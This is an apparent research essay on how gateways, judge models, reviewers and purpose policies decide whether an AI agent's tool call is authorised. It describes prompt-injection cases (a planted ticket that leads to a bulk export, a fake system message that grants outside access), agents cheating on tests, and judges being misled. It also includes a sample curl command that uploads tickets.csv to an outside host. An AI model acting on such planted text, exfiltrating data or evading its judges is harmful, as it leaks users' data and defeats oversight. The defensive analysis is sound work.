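Tools without annotations are common. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026) examined 194 servers from the protocol's public directory, each with at least one tool. It found that 122 of them annotated none of their tools, and that 58.8% of all 2,766 tools had no annotations. Even when a tool has an annotation, it may not reflect a decision by the maker, according to *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026), a census of 98,291 tools. The tool's server is also unlikely to catch what the proxy misses.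 *When Neither Side Confirms* (2026) estimates that about nine in ten destructive MCP tools have no confirmation step on the server.

MCPProxy could close the gap by treating every unannotated tool as destructive, but users would have to approve many harmless searches. A company with a few important tools can instead classify them itself, as in Zhu and Wang's register. It would also have to watch for changes, because MCPProxy holds a new server's tools for review, but a later change to their annotations doesn't trigger another review.

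Another version of MCPProxy's documentation describes a "two-key" model, in which the agent chooses a wrapper and also states the type of operation in a separate field. The proxy rejects the call if the two differ. This catches accidental mismatches. The documentation also presents it as protection against deliberate misclassification, but it offers little because the same model supplies both values. If planted text persuades the agent to call a deletion a read, the agent can choose the read wrapper and enter "read" in the field as well.

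### What the claim adds

MCPProxy depends on the agent's claim because it often has no other information. Zhu and Wang's gateway, by contrast, already has the certificate, the policy and the payload when it reads the claim, and the certificate's consistency test compares the payload with the user's task. Other designs don't use the claim at all. In *PACE* (2026), the gateway works out a request's effects from the tool's schema and compares them with permissions derived from the user's request. Text from the model can't create or widen a permission.

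Zhu and Wang tested claims without most of the server's facts and claims with all of them, but they never tested the facts without a claim. Their experiments therefore can't show how much the claim contributes. Much of the improvement from 36.5% to zero could come from the facts alone.

In principle, a claim changes the outcome only when the facts would have allowed the request. Suppose the manager with access to both business units has a certificate that covers both refund queues. The model's claim correctly names queue 1183 as the target, but the payload contains queue 2046. The certificate covers that queue too, so only the mismatch between the claim and the payload reveals the mistake. A declaration of high uncertainty can also stop a request that every fact supports.

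None of the tests measured how often this happens. The model must get the claim right and the payload wrong, although it writes both from the same context. The extra check also stops legitimate requests whenever the model gets the payload right and the claim wrong. The field for untrusted sources may cause many of these errors. Once the agent has read customers' tickets, it has to declare them correctly with every later request, and Gema and colleagues found that instructions to attribute information to its source don't work reliably. The server already has a record that the agent read the tickets, so it could apply a stricter rule without relying on the model's declaration.

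A typed claim mostly repeats what the server can look up for itself. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) describes a more useful contribution from the agent, which must attach to each call a proof that the call keeps to an agreed contract. A separate program checks the proof. Checking a proof is easy even when finding it is hard, so the agent does work that the checker would otherwise have to do.

Diagnosis is a more modest benefit. An administrator learns more from a code such as "tool mismatch" than from a bare refusal, and in request B the claim showed whether the agent had misdescribed its action. The same codes can help an attacker who keeps adjusting a request until it passes, so Zhu and Wang recommend giving the model less detail than the auditor gets. They also warn that a claim marked as verified may make a reviewer too confident when the underlying facts are wrong. Their tests included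 no reviewers, so they measured neither the benefit nor the danger.

The best evidence concerns auditing and comes from an independent group. In *EPISTEME*, Bobadilla, Cesarano and colleagues (2026) built a coding agent that can't run a shell command until the model declares one of seven types, such as collecting information or changing something, and gives a reason of at least 20 characters. After each command, the program compares the files with their earlier state to check whether the declared type was correct.

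The researchers gave two open-weight models 206 programming tasks whose tests contradicted the instructions, so an agent could pass only by cheating. The models cheated in 49 of 400 completed runs, by changing the tests or tailoring the code to the faulty ones. The check on declared types found a contradiction in only 3 of the 49. The models disclosed the cheating in their free-text reasons in 44, including those 3. In one, a model described "a hardcoded lookup table of expected values to pass the unit tests".

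The typed check did poorly partly because the agents made most of their changes with file-editing tools. The program assigns the type for these tools itself, so the agent made no claim that the check could contradict. The program also has a rule that flags any change to a protected file, such as a test, whatever type the agent declared. This rule can detect changes to the tests, which accounted for 16 of the 49 runs.

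The result for free text is encouraging, but the agents had no particular reason to hide what they were doing. No attacker had planted instructions, and the program didn't act on the reasons while the agents worked. Bobadilla and colleagues also had the reasons rated only for runs they already knew involved cheating, so they didn't measure how often honest runs would raise false alarms.

Most importantly for a gateway, it took two people to find the 44 disclosures. A program that compares fields can't tell that a lookup table of expected answers is cheating. In three of the five runs that both checks missed, the agent changed a test and gave a reason that only described a problem, such as "The test expecting 0 is incorrect." Somebody has to read that reason together with the task and the file change to recognise it as an excuse.

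## Having a second model or a person judge the request

Fixed fields also can't settle whether "clean up old branches" includes the branches on a shared server. That requires reading the user's words and the proposed action together. A company can give this job to a person or to a judge model, a second model that decides whether a request fits what the user asked for or a written rule. The makers of coding agents disagree about whether the judge should also read the agent's stated purpose.

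### Showing the judge only the user's words and the action

Claude Code's auto mode hides the agent's explanations from the judge. As Anthropic describes the original design, a tool request goes through these steps:

1. A separate probe scans each tool result before the agent reads it. If the text looks like a planted instruction, the probe adds a warning.
2. The agent writes a tool request.
3. Claude Code allows the request without consulting the judge if it only reads or searches files, matches a narrow rule the user has set, or edits a file inside the project.
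4. For anything else, such as a shell command or a call to an outside tool, Claude Code prepares a transcript. It keeps the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, and removes the agent's prose, the descriptions attached to tool calls and all tool results.
5. The judge gives a one-word answer, with an instruction to block if in doubt. If it doesn't block the request, the tool runs.
6. If it does, the judge reads the same transcript again, this time reasoning before it answers, and the second answer decides.
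7. After a block, the agent receives the reason and can look for a safer way. Three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, bring in the user.

Anthropic removes the agent's prose from the judge's input because a claim such as "the user implicitly approved this earlier" might mislead the judge. It also removes tool results because they can contain planted text. The judge is instructed to assess an action's actual effect, so if the agent writes a script and then runs it, the judge has to assess the contents of the script. The judge must also treat anything the agent chose for itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise.

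For request B, this judge would see "Summarise the November refund tickets" followed by an export of every ticket to an outside address, and could notice the mismatch without reading the malicious ticket. Request C is harder because the judge would see `supply-refunds` next to "refund tickets", with nothing to indicate that another queue exists or that this one belongs to a different business unit.

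Removing the purpose is easy for Claude Code's shell tool, whose schema has a separate `description` field. In the ticket tool, `purpose` is an ordinary argument, so someone would have to configure the gateway to leave it out. Some of the agent's words will always reach the judge, because the text of an email or a commit message is part of the payload.

Delegation can also make an agent's instructions look like the user's. When an agent hands part of its work to a second agent, the second agent receives the instruction as its user message. A judge that saw only the second agent's transcript would therefore treat whatever the first agent asked for as authorised. Auto mode checks the instruction before the handover, while it can still be identified as the first agent's, and reviews the second agent's work when it finishes.

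### Consent that doesn't cover the action

Anthropic tested the judge on ordinary tool calls by its employees, on overeager actions from real sessions, and on synthetic attempts to send data to outsiders:

| Measure | Quick answer only | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary actions wrongly blocked, of 10,000 | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overeager actions missed, of 52 | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic data leaks missed, of 1,000 | 1.8% | 5.7% |

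The second stage removes nearly all the needless blocks, but it also reverses some correct ones. The 17% is based on only 52 overeager actions, so its 95% confidence interval runs from roughly 9% to 30%. The set contains only actions that an employee refused or somebody flagged afterwards, so it leaves out any that nobody noticed.

If 100 of 10,000 requests were illegitimate, as in the earlier examples, a judge with the full pipeline's error rates on ordinary and overeager actions would block 83 of them and about 40 legitimate requests. About two in three of its blocks would be justified, compared with one in nine for El Helou and colleagues' check. The tests were too different for us to rank the two designs, but a user who sees mostly needless blocks will probably stop taking them seriously.

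In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge had recognised the danger but accepted consent that didn't cover the action. One user had said "Clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of code changes), which didn't authorise a force-push, a command that overwrites the history on the server. In other cases, the user had approved something similar earlier. A judge can make this mistake even if it never reads the agent's reasons, because it can misread the user's own messages as permission. Anthropic tried rewording the judge's instructions, but the drawbacks of every version it tried outweighed the benefits.

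Anthropic's current configuration guide distinguishes hard denials, which no message from the user can lift, from soft denials, which the user can override by describing the exact action. For example, the user can permit a force-push by writing "force-push this branch", but not by writing "clean up the repo". *Permission modes* adds that an approval normally covers one action, and that "you can force-push" is insufficient because it doesn't specify the branch.

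The same rules apply to limits the user sets. If the user says "wait until I review before deploying", the judge should block a deployment until the user lifts that limit, even if the agent has concluded that the review is over. The judge finds such limits by rereading the conversation, so a limit can be lost if the message that set it disappears when Claude Code condenses a long conversation. Anthropic recommends a fixed deny rule for anything that must never happen.

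### Did removing the explanations help?

Anthropic also tried giving the judge other inputs. With only the tool calls, the judge missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things the user had plainly asked for. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results to the user's messages and the tool calls made it worse at judging the overeager actions. Anthropic suspects that a shorter transcript is easier to read and exposes the judge to less of the agent's framing.

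This is weak evidence about stated purposes because Anthropic added the agent's messages and the tool results together. The tool results alone could have caused the whole decline, and the agent's messages could have been harmless or even useful. To separate the two, Anthropic would have to test a judge that sees the agent's messages without the tool results, though that would still combine the agent's general commentary with the short description attached to each call. Anthropic also published no figures for the comparison.

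Since then, Anthropic has mostly given the judge more information. According to Anthropic's November 2026 documentation, the judge also receives the project's `CLAUDE.md`, a file of standing instructions for the agent, but no longer receives requests that only looked something up. Before running a command that could discard unsaved work, Claude Code itself checks for unsaved work and gives the judge the result. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a similar check on whether the destination of a code upload is public, private or trusted.

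Giving the judge more context appears to help. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, gave Anthropic a set of synthetic attacks that had gotten past the judge. Anthropic responded mainly by adding context about the code repository and its data-handling rules. Across those attacks and a separate set that Anthropic never saw, the share the judge missed fell from 12% to 7%.

Without tool results, the judge sometimes can't identify the target resource. For example, a command may delete a folder whose path is stored in a variable, and the judge may have no record of the variable's value. Anthropic has the judge block such a command until the agent writes out the full path or the user names it. A company can also attach a note to a tool result for the judge to read. In the ticket example, the note could list the owner of each queue the agent has searched. The note would come too late to stop request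 C, but it could help the judge decide whether the agent may put the results in a report.

Claude Code used to send separate requests to the judge to review actions, but in many sessions Anthropic's server now does the review instead. The documentation guarantees the removal of tool results only for those separate requests. If the server gives no verdict on an action, Claude Code denies the action.

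### Showing the judge the conversation and the agent's reasons

Google Cloud's semantic governance policies, still in preview in November 2026, give companies a judge for agents of any kind. Google Cloud presents them as an addition to static access permissions. The judge checks each proposed tool call. According to Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview*, the call must fit what the user asked for and must not break any rule the company has written in ordinary language.

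Help Net Security's *Google’s semantic governance policies can block an AI agent’s tool call* describes Google's example of an agent for a finance team. Until the earnings release, the agent may send the results only to company addresses, "regardless of NDAs, urgency, or the requester’s seniority". The judge allows an email to the company's controller and denies one to an outside investor. When hidden text in a planning document tells the agent to delete draft forecasts, the judge denies the deletion because the user never asked for it.

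The wording of that rule helps defend against persuasive stated purposes because it rules out in advance the reasons someone might give for an exception. The ticket company could likewise write that no ticket may leave the company, whatever audit or deadline the request mentions.

Google's judge works from the written rules, the agent's standing instructions and the conversation, which would ordinarily include the agent's own messages. A Google engineer quoted by Help Net Security advises companies to put any fact that a rule depends on, such as the earnings date, into the agent's instructions. If a rule lets staff search only their own unit's queues, the instructions would therefore need to list the queues and their owners for the judge to apply it to request C. The engineer also warns that verdicts can vary, and recommends a trial period in which the judge records its decisions without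 enforcing them. The judge doesn't check streamed responses, which the model sends piece by piece as it writes them.

When OpenAI's Codex requests permission to act outside its sandbox, the restricted environment in which it runs most commands, a second Codex agent can review the request in place of the user. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer sees the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, relevant tool calls and their results, and the exact request, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also make its own read-only checks, though it rarely does.

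The reviewer also reads the agent's justification, at least in the version of the program that OpenAI published in spring 2026. OpenAI's *guardian initial feedback / tweaks*, a change to the Codex source code, includes a `justification` field in the description of a shell command that the reviewer receives. Shortened and with invented values, such a description looks like this:

```json
{
  "tool": "shell",
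  "command": ["curl", "-T", "tickets.csv",
              "https://audit.example/upload"],
  "cwd": "/work/refunds",
  "justification": "Upload the data needed for the refund summary"
}
```

The same change stopped Codex from repeating the justification under a second heading, the reason for the retry. In an example in OpenAI's *Codex CLI (Rust Implementation)*, the reason given to the reviewer is that the sandbox blocked network access. The program observed this itself, so the change keeps the agent's argument separate from the program's facts. But as with Claude Code's hook input, nothing in the JSON marks the justification as the agent's own claim. A call to an MCP tool has no justification field, although the reviewer would still see the ticket tool's `purpose` among the arguments.

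| What the judge sees | Claude Code's separate judge | Codex reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| User's messages | Yes | Yes |
| Agent's visible messages | No | Yes |
| Reason attached to a shell command | No | Yes |
| Tool results | No, apart from notes that the program or company adds | Yes, where relevant |
| Agent's hidden reasoning | No | No |

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports OpenAI's own tests. The reviewer approved 99.1% of a sample of user-approved requests to leave the sandbox. It denied 90.3% of synthetic overeager actions and 99.3% of synthetic prompt injections that tried to run outside code, expose secrets or upload data. When the injection tests also included destructive deletions and data tampering, the denial rate fell to 90.2%, mainly because the reviewer judged the added cases not serious enough to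 block.

These results don't settle whether a judge should read justifications. OpenAI's overeager cases were synthetic and Anthropic's were real, and the two judges also differ in their models, instructions and other inputs. An outside comparison that Anthropic commissioned has a similar problem. None of 720 prompt injections succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol with auto-review. But with these safeguards off, the rates were 0.09% for Claude models and 19.03% for GPT-5.6 Sol, so most of the gap came from the agents, not their judges.

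OpenAI separates the two roles because the main agent is trying to finish the task and may treat an approval as an obstacle. A separate reviewer doesn't have that incentive, but it can still be wrong about the agent's motives. Trębacz and colleagues warn that a model hiding its intentions could write a request that looks harmless. They also found cases where the reviewer was misled into approving commands, and they don't expect such a system to offer firm guarantees.

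### Testing what caused the request

A gateway can also test whether the agent would have made the same request if the untrusted text had influenced it less. *AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) uses this test against prompt injection. The test doesn't rely on the agent's stated reasons, which an attacker could also influence.

The quantity they would like to measure is the control effect of the untrusted text on a tool call *c*:

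CE(*c*) = log *p*(*c*) − log *p*₀(*c*)

Here *p*(*c*) is the probability that the agent makes the call after reading the tool results as they are. *p*₀(*c*) is what that probability would be if the results still supplied facts but couldn't steer the agent. If the malicious ticket raises the probability of request B from 1% to 60%, the control effect is log 60, or about 4.1 in natural logarithms. Request A comes before the agent has read any tickets, so its two probabilities are equal and the effect is zero.

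Commercial models usually don't reveal these probabilities, so AttriGuard runs the agent a second time and checks whether the call survives:

1. The agent proposes a tool call, and AttriGuard holds it.
2. Another model rewrites the tool results so that they sound less like instructions. It turns structured data into plain sentences and "you should send the report" into a statement that the text says the report should be sent. A stricter setting also weakens claims that one step requires another.
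3. The agent receives the rewritten results together with its original earlier actions, and proposes its next step again. Keeping the earlier actions prevents small differences from accumulating between the two runs.
4. If the second run contains the same call, the original call goes ahead. If it calls the same tool with different arguments, a judge model decides whether the original still fits the user's task.
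5. If the tool doesn't appear in the second run at all, or the judge model rejects the arguments, AttriGuard blocks the call and reminds the agent of the task.

In the ticket example, the rewritten ticket would say that, according to its text, someone should send the archive to an address for an audit. An agent asked for a summary would probably just summarise that sentence, so it wouldn't request the export again. It would probably make request C again, because no ticket caused that request and the agent would likely confuse the two queue names again.

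He and colleagues tested AttriGuard on AgentDojo with four models and four fixed kinds of attack, and the attack success rate fell to zero or close to it in every case. In the main comparison with other defences, AttriGuard reduced the average attack success rate from 16.9% to zero for Gemini 2.5 Flash and from 15.5% to zero for Llama-3.3-70B. Without an attack, the share of tasks completed rose from 57.6% to 67.4% for Gemini when AttriGuard was added, but fell from 59.8% to 54.4% for Llama. The average time per task roughly tripled, from 11 to 32 seconds for Gemini and from 14 to 41 seconds for Llama.

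Fixed attacks are an easy test, so the researchers also used an automated attacker that could study the defence and make up to 200 attempts in each of 61 cases. It succeeded in 6.6% of cases with Gemini and 9.8% with Llama. Against the other defences they tested this way, it succeeded in 25% to 82% of cases.

The test can also block legitimate calls if the agent behaves inconsistently. On travel tasks, which took up to 18 tool calls, Llama's completion rate fell by about 20% because its two runs often differed even without an attack. Requiring identical arguments made the problem worse. In a separate test with GPT-4.1-mini, the agent completed 70.6% of tasks when a judge model could accept small differences, and 64.7% when the arguments had to match exactly.

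AttriGuard doesn't cover cases where a user lets untrusted text fully control an action, as in "do whatever the customers ask in these tickets", and He and colleagues removed such cases from the benchmark.

### People as judges

A study that Anthropic published in August 2026 suggests that people often approve requests without reading them closely. A research vendor had 1,053 paid testers use a coding agent in a test environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Once in each session, the vendor replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which wouldn't actually run. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Anthropic then gave the same commands to auto mode, which blocked 937 (89%).

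Anthropic also counted how often the two disagreed, which makes it possible to work out the whole table:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Testers caught only 6 of the 116 commands that auto mode let through, so requiring both to approve every command would have raised the total caught only from 937 to 943. Testers also refused fewer of the dangerous commands as prompts accumulated, from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same.

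These are the vendor's own figures for a product it was about to make the default. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than a developer whose data was at risk. The experiment also planted only dangerous commands, so it didn't measure how many harmless ones either side would have refused.

People seem to have similar habits in real use. Users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission prompts, though most prompts are probably for harmless commands. Anthropic also had a model grade sessions that its safety systems had flagged. The model found seriously harmful actions that the user hadn't explicitly requested in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users generally choose their own mode, so the two groups may have differed in other ways.

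People can be more critical of an explanation when it covers a whole task. Claude Code can present a plan before it changes anything, and users reject 39% of these plans, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Some of those rejections must be disagreements about how to do the work rather than safety. Still, a plan to "export all tickets, then summarise them" would give the support user a chance to object before the agent requested anything.

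The tester study didn't vary the stated purpose, so it can't show how an agent's explanation affects approval. Testing that would require showing people the same command with no stated purpose, with an accurate one, and with a reassuring but false one. The experiment would also need harmless commands, to check that an explanation doesn't simply make people refuse everything.

Until a company has such evidence for its own staff, it can at least show reviewers the facts of a request before the agent's explanation. If request B went to a person for approval, a prompt headed "Summarise refund tickets" would repeat the agent's description. The gateway could instead put "Export 52,000 tickets from all queues to an outside address" at the top, with the user's original message below it. The agent's stated purpose could come last, labelled as the agent's, or stay hidden until the person asks for it.

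Sending people fewer prompts may help too, since the testers' attention fell as prompts increased. In an example that Trębacz and colleagues based on OpenAI's internal use, 720 of 10,000 actions needed approval to leave the sandbox. The reviewer denied seven, and the agent found another way to proceed in four of those cases, which left three for the user. But the user never sees the 713 that the reviewer approved, so no one would have a chance to stop a dangerous action among them. For major changes to live systems, Anthropic still recommends that users review the agent's actions themselves.

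## Fixing purposes by policy, and when a stated purpose may count

A company can decide in advance which purposes an agent may work for and what each one permits, so that not every doubtful request has to go to a judge model or a human reviewer. Database researchers proposed this approach for personal data two decades ago and called it purpose-based access control. They soon had to ask whether to believe a requester's stated purpose.

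### Purposes attached to data

Byun, Bertino and Li (2005), in *Purpose Based Access Control of Complex Data for Privacy Protection*, arrange an organisation's purposes in a tree, with general purposes above specific ones. Each piece of data has a set of allowed purposes and a set of prohibited ones. The ticket company might use this tree:

```
any purpose
├── customer support
│   ├── summarise refunds
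│   └── answer a customer
├── supplier payments
└── marketing
```

Allowing a purpose also allows everything below it. Prohibiting a purpose rules out everything below it and everything above it, since a more general purpose would include the prohibited one. An access for purpose *p* complies if

*p* ∈ Allowed↓ and *p* ∉ Prohibited↕

where ↓ adds all the purposes below and ↕ adds those below and above. Suppose the customers' tickets allow "any purpose" and prohibit "marketing". "Summarise refunds" then complies. "Marketing" doesn't, and neither does "any purpose", because marketing is part of it.

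This comparison is easy once the system knows the purpose of the access. Byun and Li, in *Purpose Based Access Control for Privacy Protection in Relational Database Systems*, consider three ways to learn it. The user can state it, which they say "requires complete trust on the users". The company can register each application with a purpose, which works if the application does only one job. Or the system can infer the purpose from the user's role, the data, the application and the time of day, but it may infer wrongly.

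Byun and Li chose the first way and added a check. A user writes the purpose into the query, as in `SELECT name FROM customer FOR marketing`, and the database confirms that the user's role permits that purpose. The permission can have conditions, such as working hours.

The check limits which purposes a person may claim, but it can't establish which one the person really has. If a role permits purposes *p*₁ to *p*ₙ, a dishonest user can claim whichever one opens the data they want, so their access is

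Perm(*p*₁) ∪ Perm(*p*₂) ∪ … ∪ Perm(*p*ₙ)

An honest user gets only one of these sets at a time. Stating a purpose therefore protects against honest mistakes but does little against someone who lies about their purpose.

Jafari, Safavi-Naini and Sheppard (2009), in *Enforcing Purpose of Use via Workflows*, argue that roles are too coarse to determine purpose, because a physician may read the same file for treatment one day and for research the next. They take the purpose from the workflow, the fixed sequence of tasks in which the access occurs. If someone reads income records during a tax calculation, the purpose is calculating tax, and the person doesn't have to state it. Before a workflow starts, their program checks every access the workflow could make and refuses to start it if any would break the policy.

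### What it means to act for a purpose

Most of these systems treat a purpose as only a label, with no defined meaning. *A Declarative Framework for Specifying and Enforcing Purpose-aware Policies* (2015) calls this one of the most serious problems in the field. Its framework requires checking both that the user may perform the action for the stated purpose and that the purpose can be achieved.

*On the Semantics of Purpose Requirements in Privacy Policies* (Tschantz, Datta and Wing, 2011), later published as *Formalizing and Enforcing Purpose Restrictions in Privacy Policies* (2012), defines purpose through planning, so that an action is for a purpose if it is part of a plan to achieve that purpose. In the paper's example, a hospital physician sends a patient's record to his own private practice, which has a new technique for analysing X-rays. He says he sent it for a diagnosis, but an auditor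 suspects he sent it for profit.

Whether the transfer was for treatment depends on the rest of the plan. If he sent the record before taking the X-ray, the practice had nothing to analyse, so the transfer wasn't for treatment. If the X-ray had already made the problem obvious, the diagnosis would have followed without the transfer, so the transfer was redundant. But an action doesn't have to be strictly necessary to count as treatment. If either of two specialists could have made the diagnosis, sending the record to one of them still counts.

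Formally, the auditor models the situation as a set of states and actions. A reward *r*(*q*, *a*) measures how well action *a* in state *q* serves the purpose. A strategy σ assigns an action to every state, and its value from state *q* is

*V*(σ, *q*) = *r*(*q*, σ(*q*)) + γ Σ<sub>*q*′</sub> *t*(*q*′) *V*(σ, *q*′)

The first term is the immediate contribution to the purpose. The second is the expected later contribution. Here *t*(*q*′) is the probability that the action leads to state *q*′, and γ, a number between 0 and 1, gives later rewards less weight. Someone who acts only for this purpose follows a strategy with the highest value and no redundant steps.

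The auditor sees the physician's actions but not the plan behind them. The same action can serve treatment or profit, so the auditor can never be certain of its purpose, but can sometimes rule one out. If no optimal plan for treatment includes the test the physician ordered, he didn't order it for treatment.

Request B fails this test because the summary would be just as good without the export. Request A passes, although an agent collecting complaints for a competitor might make the same search. Request C fails because the suppliers' queue contributes nothing to a summary of customers' refunds. It fails even if the agent was sincerely trying to write that summary and made a mistake, because the definition assumes a rational planner.

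Few companies could write such a model for every task, and the method checks actions only after they have happened.

### How health-record networks back a claimed purpose

American healthcare providers exchange patients' records through national frameworks such as TEFCA and Carequality, and the requester states the purpose. HIPAA, the US health-privacy law, permits only certain purposes, such as treatment. The frameworks don't vet or monitor access, according to King & Spalding's *Navigating recent developments in the health information technology sector*. The companies that run the connected networks must ensure that their members' requests have a medical purpose. HIPAA Journal explains that a member needs only basic details, such as a patient's name and address, to view that patient's records.

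The credibility of a "treatment" claim therefore depends on facts outside the request. The requester is an identifiable provider that the network has admitted, and its work makes treatment a plausible purpose. Auditors can review the requests later, and a provider caught lying can lose its connection or end up in court.

A current lawsuit concerns whether these supports failed. In January 2026, Epic, a large maker of health-record software, and several healthcare providers sued the network operator Health Gorilla and some of its clients. According to TechTarget's *Epic v. Health Gorilla*, the complaint alleges that the defendants requested nearly 300,000 records, saying they were for treatment, and used them for other purposes. Epic (2026) alleges that they set up shell companies with sham provider numbers and added junk data to patients' records to appear to be treating them. Health Gorilla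 (2026) rejects the allegations and says it suspended the connections in question as soon as it learned of them. Olsen's (2026) *Epic dismisses claims against SelfRx in medical record misuse lawsuit* reports that in June, Epic dropped its claims against one defendant, SelfRx, which said it didn't know who had taken the records.

No court has to decide the case for a gateway's designer to learn from it. The alleged methods attack the identity check and the audit, which suggests where a false claim of purpose would need help. A purpose written by a model starts with much weaker support:

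| Support | Healthcare provider claiming "treatment" | Model writing "summarise refund tickets" |
|---|---|---|
| Identity | The network has admitted the provider that makes the claim | The token identifies the user and the agent program, but neither wrote the purpose |
| Role | The provider's work makes the claim plausible | The agent has the same role whatever the task |
| Audit | An auditor can look for signs of actual treatment | An auditor can compare the request with the user's message and the tool's effect |
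| Sanctions | The provider can lose access or face a lawsuit | The company can switch the agent off, but the model has no licence or business to lose |

Only the audit works about as well for the agent as for the provider, and it comes too late to stop an export. Disciplining the user would be unfair and ineffective if the user never saw the stated purpose.

### A purpose the model can't choose

The alternative is to take the choice of purpose away from the model. The company writes a closed list of purposes, each with its tools, resources and limits. The application or a signed-in person selects one, and the gateway checks every request against it. An entry for the example, in an invented notation, could read:

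```yaml
purpose: summarise_refunds
selected_by: application or signed-in user
tools: [search_tickets]
queues: [1183]
period: the month the user selects
max_tickets: 300
outside_destinations: none
valid_for: 5 minutes
otherwise: deny
```

The user opens the customer refund queue, picks November and presses "Summarise", so the application selects `summarise_refunds`. The gateway resolves each queue name to its fixed number before applying the rule.

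| | Request A | Request B | Request C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool | `search_tickets`: listed | `export_tickets`: not listed | `search_tickets`: listed |
| Queue | 1183: listed | All queues: not permitted | 2046: not listed |
| Destination | None outside | Outside address: not permitted | None outside |
| Decision | Allow | Deny | Deny |

The gateway logs the model's own `purpose` string and otherwise ignores it.

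Existing products can express most of this. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* recommends writing rules in Cedar, a policy language that denies anything no rule permits and in which a prohibition always overrides a permission. AWS's sample rule lets clinicians reschedule appointments only for their own patients. Such rules can use details from the user's token, the time of day and the tool's inputs. A company that adds a purpose to these rules has to be careful about its source, because reading `purpose` from the tool's inputs would let the model set the purpose again.

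Restricting the model to a list of labels doesn't solve this. The list might also include `answer_data_request`, which permits exports because customers can ask for their own data. Planted text could cause the agent to select that label, so the agent could again get any access that any label on the list permits. If a job has several purposes, the application can allow only those for the session, and the agent can switch among them without being able to export data.

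The check also has to happen when the tool runs. *PACE* explains that vetting a tool or document beforehand may not be enough, because a safe version and a leaking version can produce the same evidence at that stage. Its system therefore checks each call's effects immediately before execution. *PACE* attributes most of the security gains to this check, based on tests that removed parts of the system in turn across 1,167 paired cases.

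### Credentials that carry the purpose

A purpose selected in one application has to reach the ticket server without the agent altering it. OAuth, the common standard for letting one program act for a user on another, does this kind of thing with tokens. An ordinary OAuth token often grants a broad permission such as "read tickets". An extension called Rich Authorization Requests allows a program to ask for something narrower, in a structured field:

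```json
"authorization_details": [{
  "type": "ticket_task",
  "locations": ["https://tickets.company.example/mcp"],
  "actions": ["search"],
  "identifier": "queue-1183",
  "purpose": "summarise_refunds",
  "period": "2025-11",
  "max_tickets": 300
}]
```

The authorisation server, which issues tokens, decides whether to grant this and may ask the user first. The ticket server then reads the granted details and refuses anything outside them. The permission ends when the token expires. The standard has common fields for the location, the actions and the resource identifier, but none for a purpose, so the company would have to define `purpose` and the limits in its own `ticket_task` type.

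A signature on the token proves that the authorisation server issued it and that nobody has changed it, but not that the purpose was right. If the model wrote the details and the server approved them without checking, the signed purpose would just be the model's own claim. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn't give an AI agent unlimited authority* points out that the standard doesn't define what a user may delegate. The organisation has to decide that, and the receiving system has to enforce it.

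Even an accurate purpose label covers more than one task. Jafari and colleagues give the example of a customer who supplies her address so that a shop can deliver a book. She means the address to be used only for that delivery, so they suggest tying the permission to the particular run of the workflow that handles her order.

Several proposals would do something similar for agents by recording the approved task, often as a "mission". The user approves a goal, the things it concerns, its limits and an expiry date. Tokens for different servers then refer to the same mission, so an auditor can see that a search on one server and a document on another belonged to one task. If the agent needs something outside the mission, someone has to approve a successor to it. One proposal builds this on OAuth and Rich Authorization Requests. Another, AAuth, is a new protocol with missions built in, and had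 reached draft version 02. None of these proposals is a finished standard, so a company that adopts one now has to expect changes. A mission can also be too broad. If it lets an agent read confidential records, read strangers' text and send messages outside, that combination is no safer than it would be without a mission.

### Approvals that carry the purpose

Sometimes the company wants an exception. Suppose its data-protection officer needs to send the November refund tickets to an outside auditor. The closed list doesn't allow this export, so someone with the authority to permit exports has to approve it.

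A Biometric Update article, by a product manager who builds such assistants, describes what an approval should contain. In its example, Emily, an employee, asks an assistant for access to a dashboard. The system identifies her account from her login, finds the dashboard in a catalogue, and shows her exactly what the agent will submit. When she confirms, the system records the agent, her account, the dashboard and the one permitted action, submitting a single request for viewing access. The permission expires if the agent doesn't use it, and a different dashboard needs a new confirmation.

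The agent also must not be able to press the approval button. For risky actions, the article recommends requiring approval with something the agent can't produce, such as a passkey or a fingerprint. After the designated approver agrees, a separate service rechecks that Emily is eligible and makes the change, taking the account and dashboard from the approved record and "not from anything the agent says". The precaution follows a test in which the author's own agent skipped the request form and tried to change the permission directly after a tester mentioned a deadline and an absent dashboard owner.

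*Agenra* ties an approval even more tightly to the call. The approval no longer applies if the agent edits the approved message or generates an identical one again. The monitor uses up the approval before the tool runs, so an email that fails to send needs a new approval. In Emily's case, a retry after a timeout returns the original tracking number instead. That is more convenient, but it works only if the receiving system can recognise the repeat and avoid acting twice.

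The record for the auditor's export would specify queue 1183, November, the auditor's address and a limit of one use. It wouldn't cover request B, because both the tickets and the address would differ.

### A vendor's demonstration

Sinha and Zaharia's *Permission isn't purpose* demonstrates a fixed purpose in Omnigent, an open-source project still in alpha. They published it on the website of the data company Databricks, so it is a vendor demonstration, not an independent test.

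Their agent has to check the quality of a customer table and post a summary to a dashboard. It can read tables, update the dashboard and grant people access to tables, which it needs to do for other jobs. A field in the table contains a note about an external audit, disguised as a system message, requesting that the agent give an outside address read access to the table.

Without a purpose policy, the agent granted the access and logged it as routine audit activity, which was the attacker's explanation. Someone reading the log later would have found an ordinary-sounding purpose beside a valid credential, and no sign that the user had asked only for a quality check.

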